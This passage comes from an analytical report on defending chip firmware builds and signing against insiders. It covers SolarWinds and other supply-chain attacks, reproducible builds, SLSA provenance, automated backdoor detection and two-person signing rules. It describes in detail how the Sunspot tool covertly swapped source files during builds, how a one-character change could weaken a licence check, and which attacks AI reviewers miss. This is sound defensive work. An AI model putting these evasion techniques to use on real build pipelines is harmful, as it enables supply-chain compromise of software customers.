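An insider with lasting control of a build server can tamper with each release directly, so Thompson's method is more useful to someone who expects to lose access. A build engineer could install a modified compiler and leave the company, and later releases would still contain the backdoor. The compiler might eventually stop inserting it, though, because it has to recognise the code it alters and colleagues may rewrite that code.

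### SolarWinds

In 2020 attackers replaced a source file during the build of Orion, a network-monitoring program. Its maker, SolarWinds, then signed the result and sent it to customers. The attackers were outsiders who had broken in and gained a build engineer's access. *A Study of Malware Prevention in Linux Distributions* (Vu, Dunlap and colleagues, 2024) identifies them as Russian intelligence services.

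They probably entered the company's systems in September 2019, according to Cybersecurity Dive. That October, SolarWinds sent customers an update containing test code that the intruders had modified, as Krebs on Security (2021) reported. This was apparently a rehearsal. The tool for the real attack, Sunspot, has a timestamp of 20 February 2020. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT* describes how it worked:

1. Sunspot started whenever the build server did, and checked every second for MsBuild.exe, a Microsoft program that runs builds.
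2. When it found one, it read the program's memory to see what it was building, and continued only if the answer was Orion.
3. It computed the hash of a source file called InventoryManager.cs and compared it with a stored value. If the file was not the expected version, Sunspot left it alone.
4. It saved a copy of the original and put a version containing a backdoor, Sunburst, in its place. The compiler then processed this file as usual.
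5. When the build ended, Sunspot restored the original and deleted the copy.

The malicious source was therefore in place only during a build, and a developer who opened the file afterwards would have found nothing wrong. The attackers were most careful to avoid a failed build, because developers would have investigated it. The hash check in step 3 reduced that risk. The attackers also switched off compiler warnings around their code so that it would not show up in the build logs. They gave themselves a way to stop Sunspot without interrupting a swap.

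SolarWinds signed the backdoored updates with its genuine key and distributed them through its normal update service. The security company FireEye discovered the backdoor in December 2020 while investigating a breach of its own network. This was about ten months after the date on Sunspot and about 15 months after the first intrusion. According to SC Media, SolarWinds later identified two customer support inquiries that in hindsight seemed related to the attack.

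SolarWinds told US regulators that fewer than 18,000 customers had installed an affected version. According to SecurityWeek, the attackers appear to have been interested enough in only a few hundred of them to send further malicious programs. Using the backdoor so sparingly probably helped it last.

An employee could have done the same much more easily, since build engineers have ordinary reasons to log in to the server and install programs there. But the employee would have run a greater personal risk, because few people have that access.

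### DAEMON Tools

Something similar happened to a smaller vendor, AVB Disc Soft, in 2026. Its Windows program DAEMON Tools lets a computer treat a file as if it were a disc in a drive. The security company Kaspersky (2026) found that installers on the official website had contained a backdoor since 8 April. The three altered programs had valid signatures from the developer. The backdoor was in code that runs before the main program starts, and it contacted a server that could send back commands.

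Kaspersky discovered it after about a month. The company had recorded several thousand attempted infections in more than 100 countries. Most of these only collected information about the computer, but about a dozen machines, belonging to government, scientific, manufacturing and retail organisations, received a more capable backdoor.

DAEMON Tools publicly confirmed that outsiders had interfered with its infrastructure and that installation packages had been affected "within our build environment". It released a clean version on 5 May, within 12 hours of a warning. The company had not yet established the root cause. The US government's vulnerability record, NVD's *CVE-2026-8398 Detail*, leaves open whether the intruders reached the build system or the distribution system. The valid signatures make it more likely that they reached the build system, although a stolen signing key would also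 explain the signatures.

Attackers sometimes compromise both the build infrastructure and the code-signing server. Kaspersky ICS CERT's *Supply chain attack* (2026) describes a 2025 intrusion in which a group called BO Team did this at another software developer. Investigators appear to have stopped the group before it altered any product.

### Comparing two builds of the same source

The most direct way to detect a tampered build is to repeat it somewhere else. Suppose reviewers have approved a commit of a chip's firmware. A second team, using a machine that the build engineers cannot access, fetches that commit from the repository and compiles it with the same compiler and settings. The resulting file's hash begins with 52bd, but the official build server sends the signers a file whose hash begins with 9e07.

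A and B differ, so the file awaiting signature is not the one the second machine built from the reviewed source. The company should not sign it until somebody has explained the difference. The hashes cannot show how much has changed, so engineers have to compare the two files byte by byte. They may find a different jump instruction in the licence check, or only a different date.

Harmless differences between builds of the same program are very common. When Cox compiled a program from files with two different names, the binaries differed in six bytes because the compiler had recorded the file name. Compilers and build scripts may also record the time, the folder or the user's name. If every legitimate release produces a mismatch, the signers will learn to ignore mismatches, including any caused by an insider's change.

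A reproducible build removes these differences, so that the same source and tools always give the same binary, bit for bit. Developers replace the current time with a fixed date, use the same folder names everywhere, process files in a set order and specify the exact version of every tool. An unexplained mismatch between two machines' binaries is then a serious warning. Building on a second machine would have exposed Sunspot, for example, because that machine would have compiled the original InventoryManager.cs.

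A match between A and B shows only that two machines turned the reviewed source into the same binary, not that the source is benign. If an insider got a `>=` past the reviewers, both machines would compile it correctly and the hashes would match.

A match is also weak evidence if one attacker can compromise both machines. *Frequently asked questions*, part of the industry guidelines called Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts (SLSA), warns that an attacker who finds a vulnerability in the build software could compromise every machine that runs it. A single administrator with access to both machines could also compromise them.

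### How common reproducible builds are

Most progress on reproducible builds has been in open-source software. Vu and colleagues interviewed seven maintainers from five Linux distributions and found that reproducible builds had been the distributions' main effort against malicious packages. The Go programming language's compiler is now fully reproducible, and its developers have published programs for checking this.

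Julien Malka, Stefano Zacchiroli and Théo Zimmermann published a much larger test in 2025. They rebuilt about 710,000 packages from versions of Nix, a large open-source software collection, dating from 2017 to 2023. Between 69% and 91% of the packages in each version were identical to the originals, and the share tended to rise over time. Recorded dates caused about 15% of the failures. These are good results for general software, but an insider needs only one file that does not reproduce. Even at 91%, about one package in eleven would differ without any tampering, so a mismatch in those packages could not be used to detect it.

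Rebuilding also has to become routine. Cox wrote in 2023 that "approximately no one" checks whether Linux distributions' binaries match their source. StageX, a small distribution, is an exception. According to *Reproducible Builds & Supply Chain Integrity*, several StageX maintainers must reproduce each file on different hardware before anyone signs it. A chipmaker could adopt the same rule for signing firmware.

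### Checking the compiler

Comparing two builds does not detect Thompson's attack if both machines use the same compromised compiler, because both builds would contain the same backdoor and their hashes would match. The remedy is diverse double-compiling, which David A. Wheeler described in a 2009 dissertation. He calls the earlier countermeasures "grossly inadequate" in *trusting trust*.

Suppose a company has a suspect compiler binary, *X*, and the source code that supposedly produced it. It also needs an unrelated compiler, *T*. Cox explains the procedure, which in this notation is:

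1. Compile the source with *T* to get a new compiler, *T*₁. The suspect binary played no part in making *T*₁, so it cannot have passed on a hidden backdoor.
2. Compile the same source with *X* to get *X*₁.
3. Compile the same source again, this time with *T*₁, to get *T*₂.
4. Compare *X*₁ with *T*₂, bit for bit.

If *X* has no backdoor, *X* and *T*₁ are two translations of the same program and should produce identical output from the same input, so *X*₁ and *T*₂ should be the same. If *X* contains Thompson's backdoor, it will insert the backdoor into *X*₁, while *T*₂ will be clean. Comparing *X* directly with *T*₁ would not reveal the backdoor, because two unrelated compilers translate the same source into different instructions even when both are clean.

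If the files match, either both compilers are clean or both contain the same backdoor. A shared backdoor is unlikely if different people wrote the compilers. *T* can be slow and basic as long as it can compile the source once, so a company could use a small compiler that its engineers have read in full. The test only shows that *X* matches its source, so the engineers would still have to read the source of the compiler they actually use. GCC's source, for example, is millions of lines long.

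### Obstacles in chip firmware

No public figure seems to exist for how reproducible AI chip firmware is. Chipmakers have one advantage over a Linux distribution because they choose their own tools and can require the same ones everywhere. But they also face problems that are rarer in open-source software.

**Closed compilers.** A team can rebuild firmware with a proprietary compiler if it has a second licence for the same version. Diverse double-compiling also requires the compiler's source, which the supplier may refuse to share. Using an open compiler for the security-critical parts would avoid this problem.

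Some firmware contains secret keys, and manufacturers encrypt some of it before release. The chipmaker cannot give the keys to everyone who might want to check the build, and encryption that uses fresh random numbers produces a different file each time. It is better to build a version without secrets, compare the hashes, and add the keys and encryption afterwards. That last step then needs a separate check, since it would give an insider a convenient opportunity to alter the file.

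A firmware release may include code for memory or a security controller that another company has already compiled and signed. The chipmaker can confirm that the supplier sent this code, but can't rebuild it without the source. Unless the supplier also uses reproducible builds and someone independent checks them, an insider there could plant code that both of the chipmaker's build machines would copy into the final file.

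Tools and other inputs can become unavailable or expensive during a chip's life, as a contributor notes in the Reproducible Builds mailing-list discussion *“Reproducible build” definition in OpenSSF glossary* (2025). To recheck an old release after discovering an insider, a chipmaker would need to have kept the whole build environment.

SLSA also says that closed-source companies must either show their code to several independent rebuilders, which many would refuse, or run several independent build systems themselves, which it calls "likely prohibitively expensive". The cost objection is less convincing for a large chipmaker, because its firmware is much smaller than an operating system and one more build system costs little compared with a product line worth billions of dollars. Rebuilding only the licence check would be even cheaper, but would miss changes elsewhere in the firmware.

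### Signed provenance and the SLSA levels

A company can also have its build system record what it did. This record, called provenance, might state which build system produced the file with hash B, and from which commit, scripts and settings. The build system signs the record with its own key, separate from the key that signs firmware. Before the firmware goes to the signers, a program checks that the record's signature is valid, that the hash matches the file, and that the repository, commit and settings are the approved ones. An engineer who compiled a private version on a laptop could not supply such a record. If an engineer used the test switch to leave out the licence check, the record would list the wrong setting.

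How much this proves depends on how hard the record is to fake. SLSA's *Build* sets out three levels above a baseline with no requirements:

| Level | What it requires | What it protects against |
|---|---|---|
| Build L1 | A record of how the build was done, which need not be signed | Mistakes; anyone can easily forge the record |
| Build L2 | A hosted build platform that creates and signs the record | Changes to the file after the build |
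| Build L3 | A platform that also isolates builds from each other and keeps its signing key out of their reach | Tampering during the build |

SolarWinds shows why the difference between the top two levels matters. An L2 record would probably have named the right repository and commit, because the build server started with the right source and Sunspot changed the file later. At L3, malicious code that got into one build could not persist to affect the next. SLSA's specification lists SolarWinds among the attacks its framework could have prevented, but for this case it states only that higher levels make such an attack "more difficult". This weaker claim is safer, because Sunspot ran on the build server itself, and isolating builds from each other gives little protection if the attacker controls the machine they run on.

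### Valid provenance on malicious packages

Attackers demonstrated the weakness of L2 on 11 May 2026. They published 84 malicious files on npm, the main registry for JavaScript code, under the names of 42 packages from TanStack, a family of open-source web libraries. According to SLSA (2026), an attacker first proposed a change to the project, and a badly configured automatic check ran the attacker's code with the project's own privileges. That code placed malicious files in a cache of components that different builds share to save time. When the official release build later used the cache, the malicious code found a temporary credential in the build machine's memory and used it to publish the packages.

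The provenance was cryptographically valid and named the correct repository, workflow and build platform, so a customer who checked all of these would have accepted the packages. Some reports described the records as L3, but SLSA's maintainers argue that npm's built-in provenance reaches only L2, and that an L3 platform would have blocked the attack. They have an obvious interest in blaming the platform rather than their standard, but their argument is sound on this point because the L3 rules explicitly forbid one build from placing false entries in another's cache.

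The attack's one clue outside the provenance was that both release runs that published malicious packages had failed. An alert for packages published by a failed run would have revealed the problem within minutes. A chipmaker could set a similar alert for firmware that reaches the signers from a failed or unscheduled build.

### Who controls the build platform

SLSA states that L3 prevents tampering by insiders, but this covers developers who use the platform, not the people who run it. An older version of SLSA's definitions acknowledges that a platform's administrators may be able to tamper with builds or access its secrets. At a chipmaker, a malicious build engineer may also be the platform's administrator, who could alter the firmware and have the platform sign a record that looks normal.

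Moving from L2 to L3 therefore narrows the group of people a company has to trust. At L2, anyone who can influence a build may be able to corrupt it. The smaller group with that power at L3 is easier to vet and monitor. In SLSA's GitHub example, developers reach L3 by using a shared build procedure that they cannot edit, so they have to trust whoever controls it.

A chipmaker can divide this power further. The people who write the build scripts should not administer the platform, and any change to the platform should need a second person's approval. The company could also rent a platform from a cloud provider, whose staff would know little about the firmware, but it would then have to keep its source code on the provider's servers. A stronger arrangement is to build each release on two platforms with separate administrators and sign it only if the hashes of the two builds match. Outside parties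 could run one of the platforms. A malicious build engineer would then need an accomplice on the other platform, or a flaw already in the source.

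## Automated search for planted code

Comparing builds cannot expose a flaw that is already in the source, and human reviewers miss many such flaws. Researchers have therefore built tools that search for planted code automatically. Some look for unusual commits, some compare how two versions of a program behave, and some use an AI model to read the code. An insider's change is hard to detect with any of these tools, because it comes from a familiar colleague and may not make the program do anything visibly new.

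### Looking for unusual commits

A project's history records who made each commit, when, and which files it changed. *Anomalicious* (Gonzalez, Zimmermann and colleagues, 2021) tested whether a tool could detect malicious commits from such metadata, without analyzing the code. The tool applies up to seven rules to each commit. It checks, for example, whether the commit changes sensitive files such as build settings, whether it is much larger than the author's usual commits, and whether the author has worked on those files before. The tool flags any commit that breaks a large enough share of the rules.

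Anomalicious found the malicious commit in 8 of 15 projects. Thirteen of the 15 had the same malware, which altered the same kind of build file. The researchers also tuned the tool's settings on the same projects they tested it on. The tool rated contributors as trusted or untrusted, using factors such as account age and number of commits, and all seven missed commits came from contributors it rated as trusted. A contributor counted as new for only seven days, so almost any employee of a chipmaker would soon earn the same rating.

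A later tool replaced the rules with a neural network that learns who normally changes which files, and when. Ganz, Ashraf and colleagues (2023) reported in *Detecting Backdoors in Collaboration Graphs of Software Repositories* that it found the malicious code in 15 of 19 projects, while their re-creation of Anomalicious found it in 5. But 11 of the 19 again had the same malware, and six of those 11 consisted of a single commit, so a tool that flagged everything would have got those six right.

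In the other eight projects, the network found four backdoors and missed four. Three of the four it found followed break-ins, including a 2021 attack on PHP, a programming language that many websites use. The attackers disguised the backdoor as a typo fix and committed it under a real developer's name at about six in the morning. That developer's previous 20 commits had all come after six in the evening. The backdoors it missed included those in colors.js and node-ipc, two JavaScript packages that their own maintainers sabotaged. Insiders use their own accounts, at their usual hours, on files they normally edit, so their commits contain few anomalies for this kind of tool to detect.

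The xz utils attack prompted researchers to look for warning signs that emerge over time. *Beneath the Mask* (2025) proposes watching how quickly a contributor gains privileged access, but this would be of little use at a company that gives engineers access when it hires them. Welsh and colleagues found that the attacker's account, Jia Tan, committed the final malicious files at unusual times of day, but that it also made some harmless commits at unusual times.

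Metadata may be more useful for protecting the build. When Gonzalez and colleagues ran their tool on Angular.js, a large web project, it flagged 34 of 8,978 commits, and only five changed the project's own source code. Most of the others changed build tools, settings or dependencies, and were often made by someone who had never edited those files before. Such alerts would be an easy way to bring build script changes to a second engineer's attention.

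### Comparing how two versions behave

LILY, a tool Kokkonis and colleagues published in 2026, instead tests what a changed program does, regardless of who changed it. This suits the insider problem better because an insider's good reputation does not affect how the program behaves.

LILY records system calls, which are a program's requests to the operating system, for example to open a file, start another program or send data over a network. The set of call types that a program makes while handling one input is that input's system-call profile. To check a new version, LILY works as follows:

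1. It takes a collection of inputs saved from fuzzing earlier versions. The fuzzer makes these inputs by repeatedly altering existing ones, and keeps those that reach new parts of the program.
2. It runs the saved inputs on the new version and records their profiles. These profiles define normal behaviour.
3. It fuzzes the new version for ten minutes to generate more inputs.
4. If one of these inputs produces a profile outside the normal set, LILY runs the same input on the old version.
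5. If the old version does not produce that profile either, LILY raises an alarm. It then lists the changed lines that led to the suspicious calls.

An alarm requires behaviour that is both atypical of the new version and absent from the old one. On safe commits, flagging all atypical behaviour produced false alarms in 14% of runs, and flagging all new behaviour did so in 10%. Requiring both conditions reduced the rate to 0.2%.

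Kokkonis and colleagues illustrate the method with vsFTPd, a file-transfer server. In 2011 attackers replaced its official release with one that gave full control of the server to anyone who logged in with a username containing ":)". The fuzzer eventually generates such a username, and the program responds with a combination of calls it never normally makes. LILY's report narrows 1,407 changed lines to seven, which show the program opening a remote command line.

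The main evaluation used 13 open-source programs and repeated every test 20 times:

| | Safe changes | Backdoored changes | Detection rate | False alarm rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Commits | 432 | 13 | 90% | 0.2% |
| Releases | 50 | 50 | 83% | 4.3% |

Kokkonis and colleagues conclude that LILY would probably have stopped three real attacks: the one on PHP, the one on vsFTPd, and a similar replacement in 2010 of the official release of ProFTPD, another file-transfer server. The ProFTPD case is the least certain. LILY detected that backdoor in only 34 of 80 runs on tampered releases, so a single run could easily have missed it. The researchers blame the older test programs that connected the fuzzer to those releases. They invented the other ten backdoors themselves, and most of those run commands or tamper with files, actions that system calls reveal.

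The xz backdoor is not among the three, and LILY would have struggled to find it because a fuzzer has no practical chance of guessing the signature that activated it. Jia Tan had also arranged for part of the project's fuzzing to be switched off. A fuzzer can also miss a backdoor that needs no signature, because it tests only the code it reaches. In 337 commits that changed code, fuzzing reached an average of about 32% of the changed lines.

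LILY also depends on its saved inputs. When Kokkonis and colleagues corrupted them to make the backdoors look normal, detection fell to 54% for commits and 46% for releases. A stricter mode restored the original detection rates but raised false alarms to about 2.5% for commits and 18% for releases. In many projects, senior maintainers can skip automatic checks, so the researchers suggest running LILY as a service that the development team does not control. A chipmaker would need to protect the saved inputs in the same way.

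Because LILY looks for changes between two versions, it cannot find a backdoor that both contain. The same group's earlier tool, ROSA, is better for a one-off audit of existing code. It fuzzes one binary for a short time and then for much longer, and reports behaviour that appears only in the longer session. ROSA often needs several hours and usually raises several false alarms, which is tolerable in an audit but not after every commit. Kokkonis and colleagues recommend auditing a project with ROSA once and then using LILY on each change.

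### Twenty false alarms for one backdoor

A false alarm rate of 0.2% sounds negligible, but backdoors are much rarer than that. Suppose a project makes 10,000 commits and one contains a backdoor. With LILY's rates for commits, the expected numbers are:

- true alarms: 1 × 0.90 = 0.9
- false alarms: 9,999 × 0.002 ≈ 20

Only about one alarm in 23 is real, even though the tool wrongly flags just one safe commit in 500. The network that Ganz and colleagues built wrongly flagged 0.7% of safe commits overall, which would mean about 70 false alarms per 10,000 safe commits. The rate was 10.75% when every project counted equally, because the network did badly on projects with short histories, so a new firmware project could have far more false alarms.

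Whether 20 false alarms are too many depends on how often the team changes its code. Hamsen, Serrania and Tafani-Dereeper write in *When an AI agent came knocking* that their company, Datadog, receives nearly 10,000 pull requests a week. At that pace, Datadog would have to investigate about three false alarms a day. A firmware team that makes 10,000 commits a year would have one every two or three weeks, and LILY usually points to a dozen lines or fewer, so the extra work is small compared with the value of protecting a chip.

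The greater danger is that engineers get used to dismissing alarms. After 20 false alarms they will expect the next to be false too, and the person best able to explain it away may be the insider who wrote the change. Someone outside the team should therefore have to approve the explanation before the change is merged.

Repeating the test can also help separate real alarms from false ones. The published counts imply that no safe commit triggered an alarm in more than nine of its 20 runs, while every backdoored commit triggered one in at least 13. A team could rerun each flagged commit 20 times, which takes a little over three hours of fuzzing, and first investigate those that trigger alarms most often. But the test included only 13 backdoored commits, so ignoring the other flagged commits would be unwise.

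By the same arithmetic, about 9,979 commits raise no alarm, and the expected number of backdoors among them is 0.1. The lack of an alarm therefore lowers the chance that a commit contains a backdoor from one in 10,000 to about one in 100,000. This reduction applies only to backdoors like those in the test. If a planted flaw does not affect system calls at all, the lack of an alarm from LILY provides no evidence about it.

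### AI models that read source code

An AI model can look for errors in a program's logic, which may leave no trace in metadata or system calls. Wang, Cheng and Xie (2026) tested this in *PRWeaver* on deliberate attacks rather than accidental bugs. They used an AI agent to write 208 attacks on ten real web projects, such as a way to abuse gift cards in a ticketing system, and ran each one to confirm that it worked. They then split each attack into two to eight changes, all of them needed for the attack to work.

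Six AI review systems examined the changes. The weakest was OpenCodeReview with DeepSeek V4 Flash, and the strongest was Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6.

| How the attack appeared | Detected by the weakest system | Detected by the strongest system |
|---|---|---|
| In a single change | 42% | 79% |
| Split across several changes | 47% | 79% |
| Split, with 16 ordinary changes in between | 34% | 66% |
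| Split, with each part inside a genuine change | 29% | 69% |

Splitting an attack did not make it harder to detect, perhaps partly because the reviewer had several chances to notice something. Mixing the attack with honest work did reduce detection, and by much more when three of the systems had to review everything at once. With 24 ordinary changes in the same batch, they detected 16% to 22% of attacks, compared with 50% to 60% when they reviewed each change separately. A chipmaker that uses AI reviewers should therefore give them one change at a time and reject changes that serve several unrelated purposes.

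The systems sometimes described the code correctly but failed to recognize the attack. One attack altered a "trust this browser" feature so that a stolen login token would keep working after the user reset their password. A reviewer described both relevant edits correctly, but interpreted them as a deliberate compromise between security and convenience and raised no objection.

These results have two large gaps. Wang and colleagues do not report how often the systems flagged safe changes, so nobody can repeat the base-rate calculation for those systems. The code was also almost all Python for websites, whereas firmware is often written in C, where memory errors are a major risk. In *SEVRA-BENCH*, Melo, Fogliato and colleagues (2026) found that the AI reviewers they tested did worst on use-after-free errors, and often detected the bug without identifying it as a security problem.

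Companies report better results on cruder attacks. Datadog says the AI scanner it runs on all of its pull requests detected every malicious commit in its own collection that was linked to known npm compromises. Some attacks of this kind hide their code in long strings of scrambled text, which look far more suspicious than one changed character in a comparison.

### AI models that read compiled programs

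Customers and outside auditors often have only the binary, but AI agents can now operate the tools that translate machine code back into something like source code. In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) tested how well agents find planted code this way. They hid simple backdoors in open-source network programs and asked the agents to locate them.

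The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, succeeded in 49% of tasks. On clean files, the models falsely reported problems 28% of the time. In one failure, Claude Opus 4.6 found code that passed the contents of a network message straight to the system's command line. It treated this as a normal feature and did not check where the command came from.

Later results in Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?* show fewer false alarms. At its highest reasoning setting, GPT-5.2 Codex solved 46% of the tasks and raised no false alarms, although the whole benchmark has only 33 tasks. The published results do not include the strongest models of December 2026, which would probably do considerably better.

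Such scores may also overstate how well a model would do on private firmware. *SRE-Bench*, from Columbia University's DAPLab, warns that a model may recognise a well-known open-source program from its training instead of analysing it. To avoid this, experts spent more than 5,000 hours writing 19 private programs for the benchmark. A chipmaker's own firmware would be similarly unfamiliar to a model.

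The few tests on real device firmware are informal. *No, Your Tools Are Not Enough* (2026) describes agents that identified open-source components in firmware and suggested possible flaws, but could not reliably locate vulnerabilities unless people required them to validate their findings. The agents also could not keep track of all the material they needed. One asked the researchers to buy a device for recording Bluetooth traffic so it could test an idea.

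*The Pain in the Cold Chain* (Logan, 2026) reports a more successful case. Agents from Finite State, Logan's employer, examined the compiled firmware of a supermarket refrigeration controller and found two of its three known flaws within hours, without being given any information about them. One was a login check that accepted a "code of the day" in place of a password. Anyone who knew the formula could calculate the code from the date, for any controller. An insider might plant a similar flaw in a licence check, making it accept a credential it should reject. However, Finite State sells firmware analysis, so it has an interest in the result. The case also covers only one product, and Logan gives no false alarm rate.

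### Would these tools find a weakened licence check?

In the metadata, the change from `>` to `>=` that lets a chip reuse its latest licence is a one-character edit by an engineer who regularly works on that file. An alert on every edit to the licence check would flag honest edits as well as malicious ones.

LILY would probably miss it too. Firmware on a small controller inside a chip may run without a conventional operating system, in which case there are no system calls to record. Even where there are, accepting licences is normal on a licensed chip, and the chip does the same things after accepting a used licence as after accepting a new one. LILY did detect a fixed password planted in sudo, a program that grants administrator rights, in all of its runs. A false acceptance can therefore show up in system calls, but only if it leads to calls that are not already normal.

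A firmware team could adapt the idea by recording whether the chip accepts or refuses each licence, rather than system calls. The team would replay valid, expired, reused and damaged licences on the old and new firmware versions, and investigate every licence that only the new version accepts. This would expose the `>=` but, like any test with a limited set of inputs, would probably miss a hidden exemption for one device. There seems to be no published test of such a tool.

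AI analysis of the source code is the most promising existing method for finding this flaw, since it can work even when the change looks ordinary and causes no new system calls. The "trust this browser" case suggests that the model should also have a written rule to check the code against, such as "a chip must refuse any licence number that is not greater than every number it has used". The rule would make the model less likely to mistake a weakened check for a design choice. As with Juniper's self-test, someone outside the team that writes the code should write the rule.

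No published detection rate shows how well a tool would protect a chipmaker's own licence check. The chipmaker can test a tool with planted flaws, just as it can test a human reviewer, provided it also counts how often the tool flags clean versions. The people who choose the flaws should not also tune the tool, or the test will repeat the mistake of tuning and testing on the same examples.

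## What two approvers at signing can and cannot stop

A backdoor that reviewers, second builds and automated tools all miss reaches the signing stage inside what looks like an ordinary release. Dual control, which requires two authorised people to act before a signing key can be used, is often the last human check before the firmware goes to customers. How much protection it gives depends on what those two people can see.

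### A signing session

Suppose a chipmaker is ready to release version 4.2 of its firmware. Companies' procedures differ, but Cooper, Regenscheid and colleagues (2018), in *Security Considerations for Code Signing*, describe a typical workflow. They wrote this guidance for the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) with the National Security Agency. With dual control added, a session might go like this:

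1. A release engineer submits the binary to the signing system with its version number and a record of earlier approvals. The system checks the engineer's identity and whether they may submit code for this product.
2. A program computes the file's hash.
3. Two approvers log in separately. Each typically sees a file name, a version and a hash, and accepts or rejects the request.
4. The signing system checks that the paperwork is complete. The hardware security module checks that two different authorised people have approved, then signs the hash with the production key.
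5. The system logs who made the request, who approved it, when, and which key signed which hash.

According to the *Signing Guide* for OpenTitan, an open-source security chip design, a tool first writes the public key into the binary and computes a 256-bit hash of the result. Staff would normally then take the prepared files to a secure facility for a "signing ceremony", which produces the signatures as separate files.

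Cooper and colleagues recommend reviewing the log regularly for unusual uses of the key, and protecting it so that someone who breaks into the signing system cannot overwrite old entries. They say only that a company should "consider" requiring two approvers, multi-factor authentication, or both. They separately recommend vetting code before signing it, because a signature shows that the company accepts the code. In their firmware workflow, approvers examine the code "per organization policy", which could mean reading every change or only checking the version number.

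NIST's *Security and Privacy Controls*, a catalogue of safeguards for organisations, contains two versions of the two-approver rule. For sensitive commands, it requires only that two authorised people approve. For changes to important system components, it requires two people with the expertise to judge whether the changes are "correct implementations of approved changes". A chipmaker could satisfy the weaker version with two approvers who know nothing about firmware. Even the stricter version only requires checking a release against changes already approved, so if a reviewer has approved a `>=` in the licence check, a release containing it counts as correct. NIST revised the catalogue in August 2025 to make software updates more secure, but does not list either rule among the changes.

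### Two routes to a malicious signed file

A signer could misuse the key by preparing a private version of the firmware that skips the licence check, submitting its hash for signing and giving the signed file to a smuggler. This version would not have gone through code review or the official build system. Under dual control, the signing module will not sign until a second person agrees, and that person can ask why the hash does not belong to any planned release.

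The other route is to plant code in the official release and let honest people sign it. The two approvers for version 4.2 see the right file name, the right version and a hash that matches the build server's record. All of this is accurate, so the second approver has no more reason to object than the first, and both approve.

The SolarWinds attackers took this second route. Two approvers would have seen a scheduled Orion update with a hash from the company's own build server, and would have had little reason to reject it. A second signer for xz utils would have had a better chance of catching the backdoor, but only by recreating the release archive from the repository and noticing that the build script in the archive made by Jia Tan, the malicious maintainer, had been altered.

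Cooper and colleagues list "signing of unauthorized or malicious code" as a single threat, with causes that include honest mistakes, insider attacks and break-ins. This grouping is reasonable for a short guide, but it can give readers the impression that one safeguard covers the whole threat. Requiring two approvers guards against unauthorised signing but not against malicious code that the company has unknowingly authorised.

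Dual control also leaves some ways to misuse the key. It applies only to requests that go through the module, so a thief who has copied the private key can sign files on any computer. Cooper and colleagues advise against public keys that a device can never replace, because the manufacturer could not recover from a theft. The H100 supports key revocation, according to the Nvidia brief that Petrie quotes. An administrator who can create accounts might approve a request twice under different names. Cooper and colleagues recommend that the people who administer the signing system not submit code to it.

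### How much risk the second approver removes

There seem to be no published figures for how often insiders at chipmakers misuse signing keys or plant code. The numbers below are illustrative.

Suppose one person can sign alone and has a 1% chance of misusing the key in a given year. Suppose also that planted code reaches signing undetected with a yearly chance of 0.4%. The total risk is about:

1% + 0.4% = 1.4%

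The company then adds a second approver, who also has a 1% chance of turning malicious, independently of the first. Misuse now requires both:

(1% × 1%) + 0.4% = 0.01% + 0.4% = 0.41%

Dual control removes about 70% of the risk, which is a large benefit for a few minutes' work per release. Over ten years, the chance of at least one malicious signed file falls from about 13% to 4%. But planted code accounts for nearly 98% of the remaining risk. Adding a third approver would only reduce the yearly risk from 0.41% to 0.4001%, while catching half of the planted code before signing would reduce it to 0.21%.

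The least realistic assumption is that the two approvers are independent. A malicious approver can choose a friend, offer a bribe, or wait for a colleague who approves everything. Let *q* be the chance that the first approver turns malicious, *c* the chance that the second then goes along, knowingly or not, and *p* the chance of planted code. Then:

*total risk* ≈ *qc* + *p*

In the example above, *c* was 1%. The table changes one assumption at a time.

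| Assumption | Total with one approver | Total with two approvers | Planted code's share with two |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original example | 1.4% | 0.41% | 98% |
| Second approver goes along 10% of the time | 1.4% | 0.5% | 80% |
| Second approver goes along 50% of the time | 1.4% | 0.9% | 44% |
| Planted code is ten times rarer | 1.04% | 0.05% | 80% |
| Planted code is ten times more common | 5% | 4.01% | nearly 100% |

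With the original values of *p* and *q*, misuse of the key becomes the larger risk again only if the second approver approves the misuse more than 40% of the time. That could happen without a conspiracy if the approver approves requests out of habit. NIST suggests rotating the duty among people to reduce the risk of collusion. Rotation makes it harder to cultivate an accomplice, but it does not help if everyone approves requests without checking them.

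Requiring two approvers helps more when many people have signing rights. If any of five people could sign alone, the chance that at least one misused the key in a year would be about 4.9%. The chance that at least two of the five turned malicious in the same year is about 0.1%. With the risk of planted code included, requiring a second approver would reduce the total from 5.3% to 0.5%.

The calculation also assumes that attackers don't switch between the two routes. But a smuggler who learns that no signer can act alone might bribe a developer instead. If one in ten of the attempts that dual control blocks succeeded this way, the total would be about 0.51% rather than 0.41%, so dual control would still help, but by less than calculated.

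### What the military rule requires

The best-known model for dual control is the US military's two-person rule for nuclear weapons. The Department of Defense's *DoD Nuclear Weapon System Safety Program Manual* (2014) requires at least two authorised people to be present during any operation with a nuclear weapon, unless a specific safety rule allows an exception. They "must be able to detect incorrect or unauthorized procedures" in the task and must understand the safety and security requirements that apply.

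The U.S. Air Force's *Nuclear Surety Tamper Control and Detection Programs* (2013) requires each member of a two-person team to have a reliability certification, training, and the ability to detect an incorrect act promptly. Anyone who sees an incorrect act must immediately try to stop it. Two people who both have only interim certification cannot form a team. A violation occurs as soon as a lone person has the opportunity to tamper with a weapon, even if they do not touch it.

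An approver who sees only a hash meets this standard when the task is to use the signing key properly, because they can detect an unscheduled request, the wrong version number or a hash that does not match the release record. They fall far short of it when the task is to release firmware that enforces the rule, because the hash does not show whether the licence check works.

The timing also differs. A weapons technician's partner can see the technician reach for the wrong cable and intervene. But an insider may have planted malicious code months earlier on a developer's computer, so the second approver would see nothing suspicious in the signing room.

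A chipmaker that requires two people only at signing has adopted a small part of the military rule, which applies to any operation with a weapon, including maintenance. A firmware equivalent would require two competent people for every commit, every change to the build server, and every signature.

The military also does not depend on the two-person rule alone. The manual states that safeguards cannot give absolute assurance, and calls for layers of them to reduce single points of failure. For example, the people who install certain tamper-evident seals must not also store and account for them. Under the Department of Defense's *DoD Nuclear Weapon Systems Surety Program* (2024), people with access to Sigma 14, a category of sensitive weapon data, cannot join a two-person team that could give them access to a weapon. A chipmaker could likewise bar the engineers who wrote the licence check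 from approving its release, since they know best how to defeat it.

### Three signers and one false screen

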